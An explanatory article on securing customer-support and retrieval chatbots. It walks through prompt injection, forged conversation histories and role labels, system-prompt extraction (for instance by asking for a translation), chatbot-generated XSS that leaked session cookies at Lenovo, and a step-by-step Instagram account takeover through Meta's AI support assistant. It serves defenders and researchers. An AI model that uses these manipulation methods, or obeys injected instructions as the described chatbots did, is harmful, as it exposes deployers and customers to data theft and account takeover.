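# Security of Public-Facing AI Chatbots: Customer Support, In-Product Assistants and Retrieval Systems

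## How a production chatbot works and where strangers' text gets in

A production chatbot is a chat program that a company runs as a working part of its website, product or support desk. Its replies come from a large language model, which is software trained on very large amounts of text that writes one token (a word or part of a word) at a time. The company that offers the chatbot to its customers or staff is the deployer. Most deployers rent a model from a model provider such as OpenAI, Anthropic or Google instead of building one, and many rent the chat software too. The deployer supplies instructions, documents, and connections to systems such as its order records.

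Company websites have always taken in text from strangers, through search boxes, order forms and product reviews. An ordinary program stores that text or compares it with other data. A chatbot passes it to a model that follows instructions in plain language, and the software around that model may be able to open customer records or issue refunds. Most attacks particular to chatbots depend on the system giving a stranger's words more authority than the stranger has. The best-known class is prompt injection, which OWASP, a non-profit foundation that ranks software security risks, again put first in its August 2026 list for language-model applications, although Infosecurity Magazine's *Prompt Injection Remains Biggest LLM Risk, Despite Limited Incidents* (2026) noted that few incidents have been recorded.

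### One message through a shop's chatbot

A support chatbot answers a company's customers, often before they have logged in. Tallow Lane, an invented online kitchenware shop, has one that can look up orders, change delivery addresses and issue small refunds. The shop rents it from a supplier that serves many other shops.

Ines bought a kettle there last week. Without logging in, she opens the chat window, gives her order number and email address, and asks where the parcel is and whether she can return the kettle if the lid rattles. The chat window, or widget, is a small program that the shop's page loads into her browser. It sends her message to a server in a web request.

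Who runs that server depends on the product. *When AI Meets the Web* (Kaya, Landerer and colleagues, 2025) examined 17 chatbot plugins, which are ready-made add-ons for websites. Seven, made for the site-building system WordPress, send the message to the website's own server, which contacts the model provider. The other ten send it to the plugin company, which deals with the model provider on the website's behalf. Tallow Lane's chatbot works the second way.

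The first trust boundary, a point where data from a less trusted party enters a more trusted part of a system, is between the browser and the server. The visitor controls everything the browser sends, including the data outside the text box, because anyone with modest technical skill can write the whole request by hand.

This matters most for the conversation history. Most chatbots use web requests that keep no record of earlier ones, so some part of the system has to store the earlier turns and supply them again for a follow-up question to make sense. The server or the model provider can do this, or the visitor's browser can store the history and send it back with every new message. Eight of the 17 plugins relied on the browser, and Kaya and colleagues found that none of the eight checked whether the returned history matched what the chatbot had written. A visitor could therefore rewrite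 the chatbot's side of the conversation as well as their own. The most widely used of the eight has since fixed the fault. The sample leans toward cheap products for small businesses and leaves out enterprise platforms such as Zendesk and Intercom, which the researchers thought less prone to such mistakes. Tallow Lane's supplier keeps the history on its own server.

The server now assembles the model's input. The system prompt, which contains the deployer's standing instructions, comes first. Tallow Lane's system prompt restricts the chatbot to shop business, sets a 30-day limit on returns and forbids discounts. The server also adds descriptions of the available tools, then any earlier turns, then Ines's message. Each piece is labeled with its role: "system" for the deployer's instructions, "user" for the visitor, "assistant" for the chatbot's earlier replies and, in newer models, "tool"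 for material returned by other software.

The model's training did not cover this shop's kettles. The supplier's software therefore searches a store of documents for passages relevant to the question and adds them to the input, a technique called retrieval-augmented generation (RAG). A crawler fills the store by visiting the shop's pages each night and saving their text. For Ines, the search finds the returns policy and the kettle's product page, including customer reviews, two of which mention a rattling lid.

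Those reviews are useful to her, but they also cross a second trust boundary, between whoever can publish on the shop's pages and the data store the chatbot draws its facts from. The crawlers that Kaya and colleagues tested mostly strip out a page's structure and keep all the visible text, so the layout that helps a human reader recognize a customer's opinion tends to be lost. Fifteen of the 17 plugins had crawlers that took in third-party text along with the site's own. To see how often this happens on live sites, the researchers picked 100 e-commerce sites at random from those running the most common plugin and asked their chatbots about complaints in existing reviews. Thirteen gave specific details from the reviews. The researchers regard 13% as an underestimate because they planted nothing, asked each chatbot at most five questions, and met several that refused to discuss individual customers.

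The model can only produce text, so it cannot open the order database itself to find the parcel. Instead, it writes a tool call, which is text in a fixed format that names a function and the values to pass to it. The surrounding software then runs that function. Here the model writes a call to the order lookup with Ines's order number and email address. The software runs the lookup, adds the result to the model's input and runs the model again. The result shows that the parcel left the warehouse on Tuesday.

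This exchange crosses a trust boundary in both directions. On the way out, the values in the call come from a model whose input already contains a visitor's message and several strangers' reviews. The lookup runs under a service account, which belongs to a program and often has wider access than any single user. Tallow Lane's service account can read every order in the shop. On the way back, the order record brings in more text from outsiders, because customers write the delivery notes and the gift message.

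Tsigkopoulos and Ntantogian (2026), in *From Prompt Injection to Web Exploitation*, describe the general arrangement as a model sitting between a web application's user interface and the services behind it. The model's output may become a database query, a request to another web service, or part of a page. In their analysis, the model usually gives an attacker a way to reach an existing weakness rather than creating a new one. The weakness is in a component whose programmers assumed that its input came from a trusted source.

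The last trust boundary is between the model's output and the browser that displays it. The widget displays the answer with formatting, which may include links and images. The browser loads an image by contacting the address where it is stored, so an answer can set off a network request before Ines clicks on anything. If the widget treats the answer as raw page code, a script inside it could run with the same access as the shop's own page. The answer may also reach more than one browser, because Tallow Lane copies each conversation into its helpdesk software, where an employee can open it while logged in to the staff system.

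### Why instructions and data arrive as one stream

The model receives the system prompt, the reviews, the order record and Ines's question as a single sequence of tokens, which also includes the role labels. It computes a likely next token from the whole sequence, adds it to the end and repeats. No separate mechanism sorts the sequence into commands to follow and material to consult. The US standards agency, NIST (2025), attributes many of the security weaknesses in language-model applications to this missing separation and compares it to SQL injection, a much older flaw.

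SQL is the language programs use to query databases. Suppose Tallow Lane's old order-status page built its queries by pasting whatever the visitor typed into the middle of an SQL command. A visitor who typed a fragment of SQL instead of an order number could change the command and might get back every order in the table. Parameterised queries reliably prevent this. The program sends the database a command with a placeholder for the order number. The database works out the command's structure from that template alone and treats the visitor's text only as a value. If the visitor types SQL, the database searches for an order with that text as its number and finds none.

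Prompt injection is named after SQL injection because the two attacks are similar, but David C, in *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)*, a December 2025 post for the UK's National Cyber Security Centre, argues that the comparison misleads people who know web security well. A database engine carries out instructions, and it stores data or uses it in queries. Parameterised queries work because they enforce this distinction, which the engine already makes. A language model only predicts the next token and has no such distinction to enforce, and David C doubts that prompt injection will ever have as complete a remedy.

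The system only checks whether an order number matches, but a retrieved passage has to influence what the chatbot writes, or there would be no reason to retrieve it. Tallow Lane wants the sentence about 30-day returns to change the answer, but does not want a sentence in a review to change it in the same way. Both sentences arrive as ordinary English in the same input.

Model makers have responded by training models to follow an instruction hierarchy, in which system text has priority over user text and text returned by tools has the least authority. This training helps, but it only makes models tend to follow the hierarchy, and it gives no guarantee of the kind a database parser gives. Ye, Cui and Hadfield-Menell (2026), in *Prompt Injection as Role Confusion*, measured models' internal activity and found that it tracked the style of a passage more closely than its role label. Careless software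 can also remove the benefit. Seven of the plugins in the study by Kaya and colleagues inserted retrieved web text under the "system" label, which gave a customer's review the same nominal rank as the deployer's instructions.

### Prompt injection and jailbreaking

In direct prompt injection, the chatbot's own user types instructions meant to make it depart from the deployer's instructions. For example, a Tallow Lane visitor might try to talk the chatbot into a discount that the system prompt forbids. *Design Patterns for Securing LLM Agents against Prompt Injections* (Beurer-Kellner, Buesser and colleagues, 2025) gives almost the same example, with a customer-service chatbot that quotes prices for new cars.

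In indirect prompt injection, the instructions are in content that the chatbot reads, such as an email, a form entry or a web page. Someone who never opens the chat window could write a review of the kettle that includes an instruction to the chatbot, for example to recommend a rival shop. The next customer who asks an ordinary question about the kettle triggers the instruction. The text stays in the document store and can turn up in later conversations until somebody finds and removes it.

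NIST distinguishes direct from indirect prompt injection by what the attacker needs. A direct attacker needs access to the chat itself, while an indirect attacker needs control over some resource that the system will take in while running. Direct injection is usually aimed at the deployer, whereas indirect injection often harms the innocent user whose question brought the text in. Beurer-Kellner and colleagues mention the distinction in a footnote and choose not to use it, which is reasonable because they look for designs that hold up wherever the hostile text comes from. The distinction is still useful to a deployer trying to work out who could attack a particular chatbot.

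Jailbreaking targets the model maker's own rules. A visitor who uses Tallow Lane's chat window to extract instructions for making a weapon is trying to get round limits the provider trained into the model. The shop is a bystander, though screenshots of the exchange could embarrass it. Kaya and colleagues distinguish jailbreaking from prompt injection by the number of parties involved. Jailbreaking involves two, the model provider and a user it does not trust. Prompt injection adds a third, an application developer with its own instructions, and the untrusted party may be either the user or an outside source of data.

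Writers disagree on how to distinguish prompt injection from jailbreaking. The software developer Simon Willison coined the term "prompt injection" in September 2022. *Prompt injection*, a collected series of Willison's blog posts (2025), limits the term to attacks on applications that join trusted and untrusted text together. In *The lethal trifecta for AI agents*, Willison complained that many people now take it to mean typing something clever into a chatbot to embarrass its maker, which Willison calls jailbreaking. NIST uses a broad class of "direct prompting attacks" that includes both jailbreaks and direct prompt injection. The attacks also overlap in practice. Chat products keep some of their safety rules in a system prompt, so prompt injection can defeat those rules, and jailbreaking techniques can defeat a filter that itself relies on a language model.

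Asking whose rule the attack breaks, the model maker's or the deployer's, usually settles a case. The answer affects what a deployer should buy. Willison warns that a detection product trained on jailbreaks may catch a request for a napalm recipe but miss a request to forward the latest sales figures to an outside address. At Tallow Lane, a request to send a parcel to a new address contains nothing that a model maker would forbid. It is harmful only if the person asking has no right to redirect the parcel, and the wording alone cannot show whether they do.

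### The confused deputy

Security engineers called this problem of rights the "confused deputy" long before chatbots. A confused deputy is a program with legitimate authority that is induced to use it for someone who lacks it. The term comes from *The Confused Deputy* (Hardy, 1988), a short paper that recounts a "nearly true" story from Tymshare, which sold time on shared computers.

Tymshare's customers could run a compiler and name a file for its debugging output. The compiler also recorded statistics on how people used the programming language. It wrote these to a file in SYSX, the system directory where the compiler was stored, so Tymshare's staff had given it permission to write there. The company's billing records were in the same directory. One customer learned the name of the billing file and gave it as the file for the debugging output. The operating system checked whether the compiler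 was allowed to write there, found that it was, and let it overwrite the billing records.

Hardy cannot find a faulty line of code. The compiler could not refuse file names in other directories, because customers had good reasons to put output there. A rule against the billing file's name would leave every other sensitive file exposed. The problem arose because the compiler had authority from both the customer who started it and the staff who installed it, and could not indicate which authority a given request relied on. Tymshare first added a way for a program to switch between its two authorities, but some applications soon needed more than two. Hardy prefers to use capabilities, which are tokens that each identify a particular file and grant permission to use it. The customer would give the compiler a capability for the output file instead of a name, and a customer with no right to the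 billing file would have no capability for it.

Tallow Lane's order lookup works the same way. The service account can read every order because the chatbot serves every customer, but a question from Ines should use only her right to see one order. If the lookup accepts any order number the model writes, the database receives a valid request from an account with full rights, and nothing in the request shows whether it was made for the shop, Ines, or the author of a review.

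Any sentence in a chatbot's input might misdirect the model, whereas a customer could misdirect the compiler only through the one value it accepted as a file name. David C calls the language model an "inherently confusable deputy" because engineers can fix a classical confused deputy but can only limit the damage from a language model. Designers should therefore ask, for each tool a chatbot can call, what would happen if an attacker could call it directly.

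### Support chatbots, in-product assistants and retrieval chatbots

Tallow Lane's chatbot serves the public, but other production chatbots serve employees or paying users, and their exposure differs. An in-product assistant is built into software and can read what its logged-in user can read. Willison's standard example is an email assistant that can search a person's inbox, summarise messages and send replies. A retrieval chatbot answers questions from documents such as manuals or a staff handbook. The table gives the usual arrangement for each.

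| | Support chatbot | In-product assistant | Retrieval chatbot |
|---|---|---|---|
| **Who can write to it** | Anyone who opens the website, often without logging in | The logged-in user; indirectly, anyone who can send that user an email, an invitation or a shared file | Whoever may ask questions; indirectly, anyone who can add or edit a document in the store |
| **What it reads** | The chat, help pages, product pages and the records its tools return | The user's messages, files, calendar and business records | Passages that the search selects from the document store |
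| **Whose authority it uses** | Usually a service account that covers all customers | Usually the logged-in user's own permissions | Usually the account that built the index, sometimes narrowed to what the person asking may see |
| **Who sees the output** | The visitor, and staff who later open the conversation | The user, and anyone to whom the assistant sends something | The person who asked, whether a member of staff or of the public |

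The indirect writers in the first row are easy to overlook. Anyone who knows the owner's address can put text in front of an email assistant, even though only the owner can type to it. The third row shows where each kind of chatbot is likely to go wrong. A support chatbot may carry out a request for one customer that only another customer should be able to make. An in-product assistant that uses its owner's permissions avoids that mistake, but a hostile email in the inbox can reach an assistant that can read everything its owner can. With a retrieval chatbot, much depends on whether documents kept their original permissions when they were copied into the index.

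These are roles more than product types, and one product can fill all three. Tallow Lane's chatbot is both a support chatbot and a retrieval chatbot, because it answers the public from a document store. The same supplier also sells the shop an assistant inside the helpdesk software, which summarises customers' conversations for employees and drafts replies using the employees' permissions. When Ines types into the chat window, she is the chatbot's user, and any instructions in her message would count as direct prompt injection. When an employee later asks the assistant to summarise the day's open cases, the assistant reads Ines's message as part of its source material. The same instructions would then count as indirect prompt injection, and the assistant could act on them with the employee's permissions.

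## What an anonymous visitor can do through the chat window

An attacker who has only Tallow Lane's public chat window starts with no account and no way to edit the shop's pages. They can send any text as often as the server allows, and they can change every part of the web request that carries it. With this access, they can try to extract the system prompt, use the model for their own work at the deployer's expense, make the chatbot say something costly or false, or get a web page to run hostile code. The first three mostly harm the deployer. Hostile code can also harm other people, including the employee who later opens the conversation.

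### Forged conversations

Kaya and colleagues at the University of California, Santa Barbara, studied more than 10,000 websites, about 8,000 of which ran one of the eight plugins that accept a conversation history from the visitor's browser without checking it. They found the sites by searching a public archive of web pages for traces of each plugin. They also installed the plugins on their own test site, where they recorded and altered the traffic between browser and server.

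If Tallow Lane used any of these eight plugins, Ines could edit an earlier reply so that the chatbot appeared to have already agreed to something. With seven of them, she could also add a message labeled "system". The model would receive her message alongside the shop's real system prompt, with nothing to show which one the shop wrote.

An attacker who can change a message's role label undoes much of the benefit of the instruction hierarchy. Models learn the hierarchy from examples of user messages that try to override the system prompt, so they learn to distrust such instructions when they are labeled "user". Kaya and colleagues point out that changing the label, which can be a single token, produces an attack that the training didn't cover.

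To measure the effect, the researchers built a simulated sales chatbot for a water bottle brand and ran it on 11 models from OpenAI, Anthropic and Google, all released in 2024 or 2025. They used three system prompts based on prompts found on real sites. The loosest prompt set no strict limits on unrelated tasks, and the strictest explicitly banned programming. Their goals included extracting the system prompt and getting the chatbot to write a short program. They tried each combination ten times, with the hostile instructions either in a forged message or in an ordinary message from the visitor. The table averages their results over the three system prompts.

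| Goal and models | Forged system message | Forged chatbot reply | Ordinary visitor message |
|---|---|---|---|
| **Extract the system prompt:** OpenAI (5 models) | 58% | 31% | 4% |
| Anthropic (3 models) | Not tested | 11% | 0% |
| Google (3 models) | Not tested | 86% | 29% |
| **Get a program written:** OpenAI (5 models) | 61% | 25% | 0% |
| Anthropic (3 models) | Not tested | 22% | 0% |
| Google (3 models) | Not tested | 74% | 12% |

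The table has gaps because Anthropic's and Google's models accept only one system message, at the start, so adding another usually produces an error. Kaya and colleagues put the gain from forging at three to eight times. For unauthorized tasks such as programming, they report success rates of roughly 25–100% when a plugin breaks the boundaries between roles and roughly 0–25% when it keeps them. When the system prompt explicitly banned programming, forged chatbot replies never got the OpenAI or Anthropic models to write a program, but forged system messages still succeeded about a quarter of the time on OpenAI's models. All 11 models are old by late-2026 standards, so the results are better evidence that role labels matter than of how often an attack would work today.

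Ordinary web engineering can fix this fault. The server can keep the history, or attach a cryptographic signature to each message and reject any message whose signature no longer matches. The researchers reported the fault to all eight makers in October 2024. The maker of the most widely used plugin moved the history to its server by December. Another said that some of its customers' workflows depend on modifying messages, and only added a logged warning. The other six had not fixed the fault when the paper came out.

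Signing chat messages helps only if the server checks every signature. The chatbot of Eurostar, the cross-Channel train operator, sent the whole conversation with every turn and signed messages that had passed a content filter, but the server verified only the newest message's signature. *Eurostar's Chatbot Goes Off the Rails, Security Firm Finds* (Willing, 2025) describes how Ross Donald of the security-testing company Pen Test Partners exploited this by sending a harmless final message, which passed the filter, and rewriting the earlier ones. The model treated the rewritten messages as trusted context and revealed its system prompt and the name of the underlying model. Kaya and colleagues had expected this kind of mistake mainly in cheap plugins for small businesses, but the Eurostar case is a reason to doubt that larger companies avoid it.

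### Extracting the system prompt

Kaya and colleagues also tried to extract system prompts from chatbots on 300 live websites, picked at random from those running the most common plugin. A plain request worked on 1% of them, a forged system message on 56%, and a forged chatbot reply on 55%. In total, 219 chatbots (73%) revealed a system prompt. Every request included the researchers' contact details and a way to opt out.

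The researchers didn't have the real system prompts to compare with, so they counted a reply as a success if at least three of its sentences read like part of a system prompt, for instance by giving the chatbot a role or forbidding something. A model that invented a plausible system prompt would pass that test. Models probably invented few of the extracted texts, though, because 76% of the texts closely followed known templates, mostly the plugin maker's own, and 31% were exact copies. The plugin's maker has since closed the route that the 73% figure describes.

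Without forged messages, a visitor has to persuade the model. Serpa, Rocha and Pedrini (2026), in *Eight in Ten LLMs Leak System-Prompt Secrets*, tested how well models resist persuasion. They put a random 16-character code in a system prompt and told the model never to reveal it in any form. An AI agent, steered by a human researcher, then tried to persuade 363 models to reveal the code. The models were listed by OpenRouter, a service that gives access to models from many makers. A model failed if the exact code appeared in any reply.

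In total, 296 models revealed the code and 50 did not. The remaining 17 could not be tested, for example because they produce only audio. A single request to translate the instructions into French got the code from 116 models, even though the system prompt specifically prohibited revealing it through translation. Another 67 revealed it when asked to rewrite the instructions in simpler English. Well over 2,000 further conversations with the last models, using many kinds of trick, got it from only one more.

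The 50 models that resisted this attack included most of the newest ones from the large American companies, such as Claude Fable 5.1, GPT-6 Astra and Gemini 3.8 Flash. The attack worked on slightly older or cheaper models, such as GPT-5.4 mini, Claude Haiku 4.5 and Gemini 3.5 Flash. The choice of model therefore makes a large difference to whether the attack works, and a support desk that handles many conversations has a financial reason to choose a cheaper one.

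The two studies report very different figures, 1% for a plain request in Kaya and colleagues' study and 82% in Serpa and colleagues', because they measured different things. Kaya and colleagues sent each live chatbot one unsophisticated request. Serpa and colleagues kept trying new approaches and needed only one success per model, so their figure is a poor guide to a given visitor's chance of success. They also tested models without the filters that a product may add. But their agent could not forge the conversation history, so a model that resisted it might still fail on a site where visitors can write system messages.

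### When a leaked system prompt does harm

Many engineers do not regard a leaked system prompt as a security problem. Anthropic publishes the system prompts of its own consumer apps, and a shop's instructions to be polite and discuss only kettles are of little use to an attacker. The prompts that Kaya and colleagues extracted mostly support this view. Where deployers had changed the template, they had usually added a name for the chatbot, a tone of voice, or business details such as an address. The researchers found no sensitive, non-public information in these common changes. Four of the 17 plugins sent the deployer's system prompt to every visitor's browser in plain text, so visitors could read it without tricking the model.

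That reassurance is limited because the sample came from one plugin, used mostly by small organizations, and most of the chatbots could only answer questions. OWASP, in guidance that Serpa and colleagues quote, warns that system prompts sometimes contain database passwords or API keys, which are codes that let a program use a paid service. Serpa and colleagues use their own 16-character code to illustrate how the harm depends on what leaks. Leaking that code proved only that the model had not followed an instruction. If it had been an API key, anyone who read it could have run up bills on the owner's account. If it had been the password to a customer database, the leak could have led to a data breach.

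Rules can be as damaging to reveal as credentials. Suppose Tallow Lane's system prompt tells the chatbot to give trade customers a 20% discount code and to refund broken items under $40 without asking for a photograph. A visitor who reads this knows what to claim and how much to ask for. Hiding the prompt would not solve the problem, because customers could find the same gap by accident or by trial and error. The shop relies on the model to decide who is a trade customer, and a visitor who can get a model to reveal a secret may be able to get it to break other rules too. The software that issues the discount can make this check more reliably by looking up whether the account belongs to a business.

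A system prompt may also describe the chatbot's tools, so an attacker who reads it can learn which functions exist and what values they accept. Kaya and colleagues could often learn this without questioning the model. The most common plugin listed a chatbot's active tools in the web page's code, and its network traffic showed the values passed to each tool and the raw results.

A deployer can test this by asking whether it could publish the system prompt tomorrow without changing anything else. If so, a leak would be embarrassing at most. If the company would have to replace a key or rewrite its refund policy, the prompt contains something that belongs elsewhere. OWASP similarly advises against treating a system prompt as a secret or using it as a security control. Even a harmless prompt can help an attacker slightly. Eurostar's instructed the chatbot to write its replies in HTML, which is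 a useful detail for anyone planning to inject code.

### Free use of a paid model

The deployer pays for every reply, and the model behind a kettle shop's chatbot can usually also write software or do homework. About 97% of the system prompts that Kaya and colleagues extracted included an instruction to refuse questions outside the chatbot's job. Their simulation used programming as the forbidden task because support chatbots rarely need it and models are good at it. As the table shows, forged messages often got the chatbot to do the forbidden task, while ordinary messages usually failed.

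Older products did worse. In a 2023 study cited by Serpa and colleagues, 31 of 36 commercial applications were vulnerable to an attack called HouYi. The consequences included theft of system prompts and unrestricted use of the model. Ten vendors confirmed the problem.

There is less evidence of people doing this for gain. After the researchers' report, the maker of the most common plugin added an explicit ban on programming to its templates. Kaya and colleagues think the maker was probably responding to abuse its customers had reported, but they don't say how many cases there were or what they cost. One visitor's programming question costs a shop almost nothing, but a script that sends thousands of questions is expensive. A limit on messages per visitor would mostly prevent that.

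Some products lack such a limit. When the security company Quarkslab audited an application built on a language model, nothing capped its use, so the auditors could send a long list of attack prompts and study the replies. Without a limit, a small deployer could also lose its chatbot. When Kaya and colleagues spot-checked 200 websites, 13 chatbots had stopped working because their owners had used up their allowance with OpenAI. The researchers attributed this to poor maintenance, but an attacker could exhaust an allowance on purpose and leave customers without a chatbot.

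One plugin, active on more than 130 sites, made the theft much easier. It contacted OpenAI directly from the visitor's browser, so it sent the site owner's API key to every visitor. Anyone who copied the key could use the model outside the chatbot, where the system prompt's instructions did not apply. The plugin's maker has only partly fixed this.

### Costly or false answers

The best-known example of a costly answer is a 2023 prank on the website of Chevrolet of Watsonville, a car dealership. As Serpa and colleagues recount, a visitor told the sales chatbot to agree with anything the customer said. The chatbot then accepted an offer of $1 for a 2024 Chevrolet Tahoe and called the deal legally binding. The chatbot's supplier took it down.

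The chatbot could not sell a car, so the only result was a reply that was widely shared as a screenshot. The damage from a false answer depends on what happens afterwards. If a Tallow Lane visitor gets the chatbot to promise a free kettle, the shop loses a kettle only if an employee honors the promise or software acts on it automatically. If an attacker makes the chatbot say something offensive, only the attacker sees it unless they publish it.

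Such a dispute is harder to settle when the visitor can forge the conversation history. The records that the eight vulnerable plugins gave website owners showed no sign of an attack. They displayed the chatbot's original greeting even when the visitor had replaced it, and they omitted all system messages, real or forged. A shop owner checking a complaint would see the chatbot's promise but not the false message that had produced it.

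The bigger risk is that a false answer reaches someone who trusts it. Donald warned that Eurostar's chatbot could have displayed a link to a fraudulent site inside what looked like an official reply. To deceive someone, an attacker would have to make that reply appear in another person's browser, not just in their own chat window, which is sometimes possible through the chat software.

### Getting a page to run hostile code

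In cross-site scripting (XSS), an attacker inserts text into a web page that runs as code in the browser of anyone who opens the page. The code can often read what is on the screen, send requests as the logged-in user, and copy the session cookie, which the browser sends to show that the user has already logged in. An attacker with that cookie may be able to take over the account without a password.

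Websites have long defended against this by displaying visitors' text strictly as text. If a customer puts a script in a product review, other customers see the code, but it doesn't run. Chatbot developers often want replies to include links and bold type, so they let the page treat the model's answer as HTML, the language of web pages. An attacker can then ask the model to write HTML that contains a script. When the page inserts the answer, the browser can't distinguish the attacker's script from one the shop intended.

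Tsigkopoulos and Ntantogian discuss a demonstration in which a visitor sent DeepSeek's chatbot an encoded script and asked the model to decode it. The script appeared in readable form only in the reply, so a filter that checked incoming messages for scripts could have missed it. The page displayed the reply as HTML, which let the script read the token that kept the user logged in. The script would not have run if the page had displayed the reply as plain text.

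The simplest form of cross-site scripting through a chatbot affects only the person who typed the message. Security teams call this self-XSS and usually rate it as minor. The attack becomes serious when the system saves the chatbot's answer and someone else opens it, which can happen whenever the chatbot hands a conversation to a human.

Lenovo's support chatbot, Lena, had that weakness. Cybernews' *Lenovo “Lena” AI Chatbot Exploited via XSS Prompt Injection* (2025) describes how Cybernews researchers attacked it with one message of about 400 characters. They opened with an ordinary question about a laptop. They then asked for the reply in several formats, in the order Lenovo's server expected, and told the model to include an image from an address that did not exist. When the image failed to load, the browser ran a second part of the image's code, which sent the browser's cookies to a server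 the researchers controlled.

Lenovo's server saved the reply in the conversation history. The attacker could then ask to speak to a person. When a support agent opened the conversation, the agent's browser would try to load the missing image, fail, and send off the agent's cookies as well. Browsers stop scripts from reading any cookie that the website has marked as off limits to them, so the cookies the researchers captured cannot have been marked this way.

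Cybernews showed that the chatbot would write the code, that Lenovo's system would store and run it, and that live session cookies reached an outside server. It did not report logging in with a stolen cookie or reading any customer's data, but said an attacker could have done both next, which is plausible with an agent's valid cookie. Cybernews also suggested that an attacker might run commands on company computers and move through the network. This is more speculative, because a script in a web page normally cannot do that without another flaw, and the researchers wrote of these steps, "We didn't attempt any of this." According to ITPro's *Flaw in Lenovo's customer service AI chatbot*, they reported the problem on July 22, 2025, the day they found it. Lenovo acknowledged the report on August 6 and had dealt with the flaw by August 18. It told Cybernews that the flaw was a cross-site scripting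 vulnerability and that customers had not been at risk.

At Eurostar, Donald demonstrated only self-XSS, since the code ran only in his own browser. Once he had got past the content filter, he could make the chatbot return any HTML, and the chat window displayed it without removing scripts. The server also didn't properly check conversation and message identifiers, and accepted simple made-up strings. Donald thought this might let an attacker's saved message load in another customer's chat, but he did not test it. City AM's *Eurostar’s new AI chatbot left customers exposed* quotes a spokesperson who said that the chatbot had no access to other systems and that no sensitive customer data was at risk. Pen Test Partners reported nothing that contradicts this.

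The flaws in Eurostar's chatbot were real, but they gave an attacker very little because the chatbot could only answer general questions. Willing reports that Donald was more worried about what would happen if the company later connected it to bookings or loyalty accounts. The company's handling of the report was arguably the more immediate problem. Eurostar did not answer the first message, which City AM dates to June 11, 2025, or a reminder a week later. When Pen Test Partners contacted Eurostar's head of security through LinkedIn, the company at one point suggested that the researchers were attempting blackmail. It eventually fixed the flaws.

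Tallow Lane's setup is closer to Lenovo's than to Eurostar's, because employees can open visitors' conversations in the helpdesk software. If that software displays saved replies as HTML, an anonymous visitor's code runs there, even if the public chat window safely shows the same reply as text.

Attackers can also combine several modest flaws. Quarkslab's auditors noticed that the application they were testing displayed images when a reply contained the right formatting, then combined prompt injection with ordinary web bugs to gain administrator access. SecurityInfoWatch's *Retailer's AI Shopping Assistant Found Vulnerable to Five-Stage Exploit Chain* (July 2026) reported a similar chain that Rein Security's researchers found in a major retailer's shopping assistant. Rein Security says the chain could have let attackers bypass the assistant's security controls. It has not named the retailer,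 so outsiders cannot check how much of the chain would have worked against real customers.

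## Identity checks when a chatbot can change accounts

When a support chatbot can change customers' accounts, an attacker may only have to claim to be a customer to act as that customer. An attacker who exploited Lenovo's chatbot would have had to steal an employee's cookie to act as somebody else.

Before a company acts on a request, it has to establish who is making it (authentication) and decide what that person may see or do (authorization). Suppose someone opens Tallow Lane's chat window, gives Ines's order number and email address, and asks the shop to send her kettle to a different house. Ines may redirect her own parcel, so the shop's authorization rule is sound. But the shop has no good evidence that it is dealing with Ines, because a flatmate could have copied both details from her order confirmation.

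A chatbot can't verify a user's identity from the conversation, because everything in it comes from the person whose identity is in doubt. Other software has to do the check and pass the result to the model.

That check is often a one-time code. The software sends a short number to an email address or phone number, and the customer repeats it in the chat. A correct answer proves that the customer can read messages sent to that address or number. It connects them to the account only if the address or number was on the account before the conversation began, because anyone can receive a code at one they supply themselves.

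Account recovery is the hardest case. The customer has lost the password, and perhaps the phone or the mailbox too, so the company has to accept evidence that it doesn't ask for at login.

### How attackers took over Instagram accounts

Meta, which owns Instagram, had been using more AI in account recovery for some time. Meta said in *Making it Easier to Access Account Support on Facebook and Instagram* (2025) that its systems had become better at recognizing people's usual devices and locations, and that locked-out users could record an optional selfie video as further proof of identity. Meta was also testing an AI support assistant on Facebook.

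Meta launched the assistant widely on March 19, 2026 (Meta, 2026). It could reset Facebook passwords, and Meta promised the same for Instagram. It typically replied in under five seconds. Meta had also started offering it to some people in the United States and Canada who couldn't log in to Facebook or Instagram. In those cases, the assistant had to deal with an account before the person asking for help had shown that they owned it.

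Attackers then used an AI recovery tool to take over real Instagram accounts, including the dormant account of the Obama White House and that of a senior US Space Force official. Hackers shared videos of the method at the end of May. Koebler (2026), in *Hackers Simply Asked Meta AI to Give Them Access*, Franceschi-Bicchierai (2026), in *Hackers hijacked Instagram accounts by tricking Meta AI support chatbot*, and Krebs on Security (2026) describe much the same steps:

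1. The attacker found out roughly where the account's owner lived and used a VPN, a service that disguises where a connection comes from, to appear to be nearby.
2. They started a password reset for the account and chose to chat with the support assistant.
3. They asked the chatbot to link a new email address to the account.
4. The chatbot sent a one-time code to the new address, and the attacker typed the code into the chat.
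5. The chatbot offered a password reset. The attacker chose a new password and logged in.

TechCrunch confirmed that the mailbox in one video had received the code. The VPN was meant to avoid Instagram's automatic protections, which treat an unfamiliar location as a warning sign. In its March announcement, Meta had credited a separate AI system with stopping a takeover by detecting a new location, a changed password and profile edits together, but a VPN hides the new location.

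Some of the attackers wanted publicity and posted pro-Iranian messages. Others wanted short usernames, which sell for thousands of dollars. Koebler saw long lists of these usernames on the messaging service Telegram, with the city associated with each account. The person who posted one list warned that the method worked on only some of the names.

Meta described the incident in letters to state attorneys general. Its *Incident Notification* (2026), sent to Nebraska on June 5, calls the tool "High Touch Support" and explains that locked-out users could ask it to email them a password reset link. The system should have rejected any address that didn't match the one on the account, but because of a bug, it sent the link anyway.

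In the videos, the attacker asks the chatbot to add an address to the account, and the chatbot confirms the address with a code. Meta's letter mentions neither step, though Meta may have left out detail that a legal notice didn't need. The difference matters because a system that emails a link to the wrong address has failed to compare two addresses, while a system that adds a stranger's address to an account has made a change that should require proof of ownership first.

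The dates are also uncertain. The Maine Attorney General's *Data Breach Notices* (2026) date the breach to April 17 and Meta's discovery of it to May 31. Koebler found that one Telegram channel had posted about the vulnerability at the end of March. If that post described the same flaw, either few people used it at first or the earliest victims are missing from Meta's count.

Meta told Maine that the breach affected 20,225 people. In its letter to Nebraska, Meta reported 37 people affected there and explained that it had counted users whose passwords the tool had reset, who had no two-factor authentication, and whose accounts an outsider had probably entered. Meta called the Nebraska figure an upper bound because some owners may have used the tool to get back into their own accounts. The national figure presumably has the same limitation.

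Isaac and Tan (2026), in *In AI blunder, more than 34,000 Instagram accounts were attacked*, report from internal Meta documents that about 34,000 accounts were affected and that attackers breached 20,000 of them. Attackers changed the usernames of more than 3,500. An owner recovering their own account would not normally change the username, so the number of real takeovers is probably between 3,500 and 20,225.

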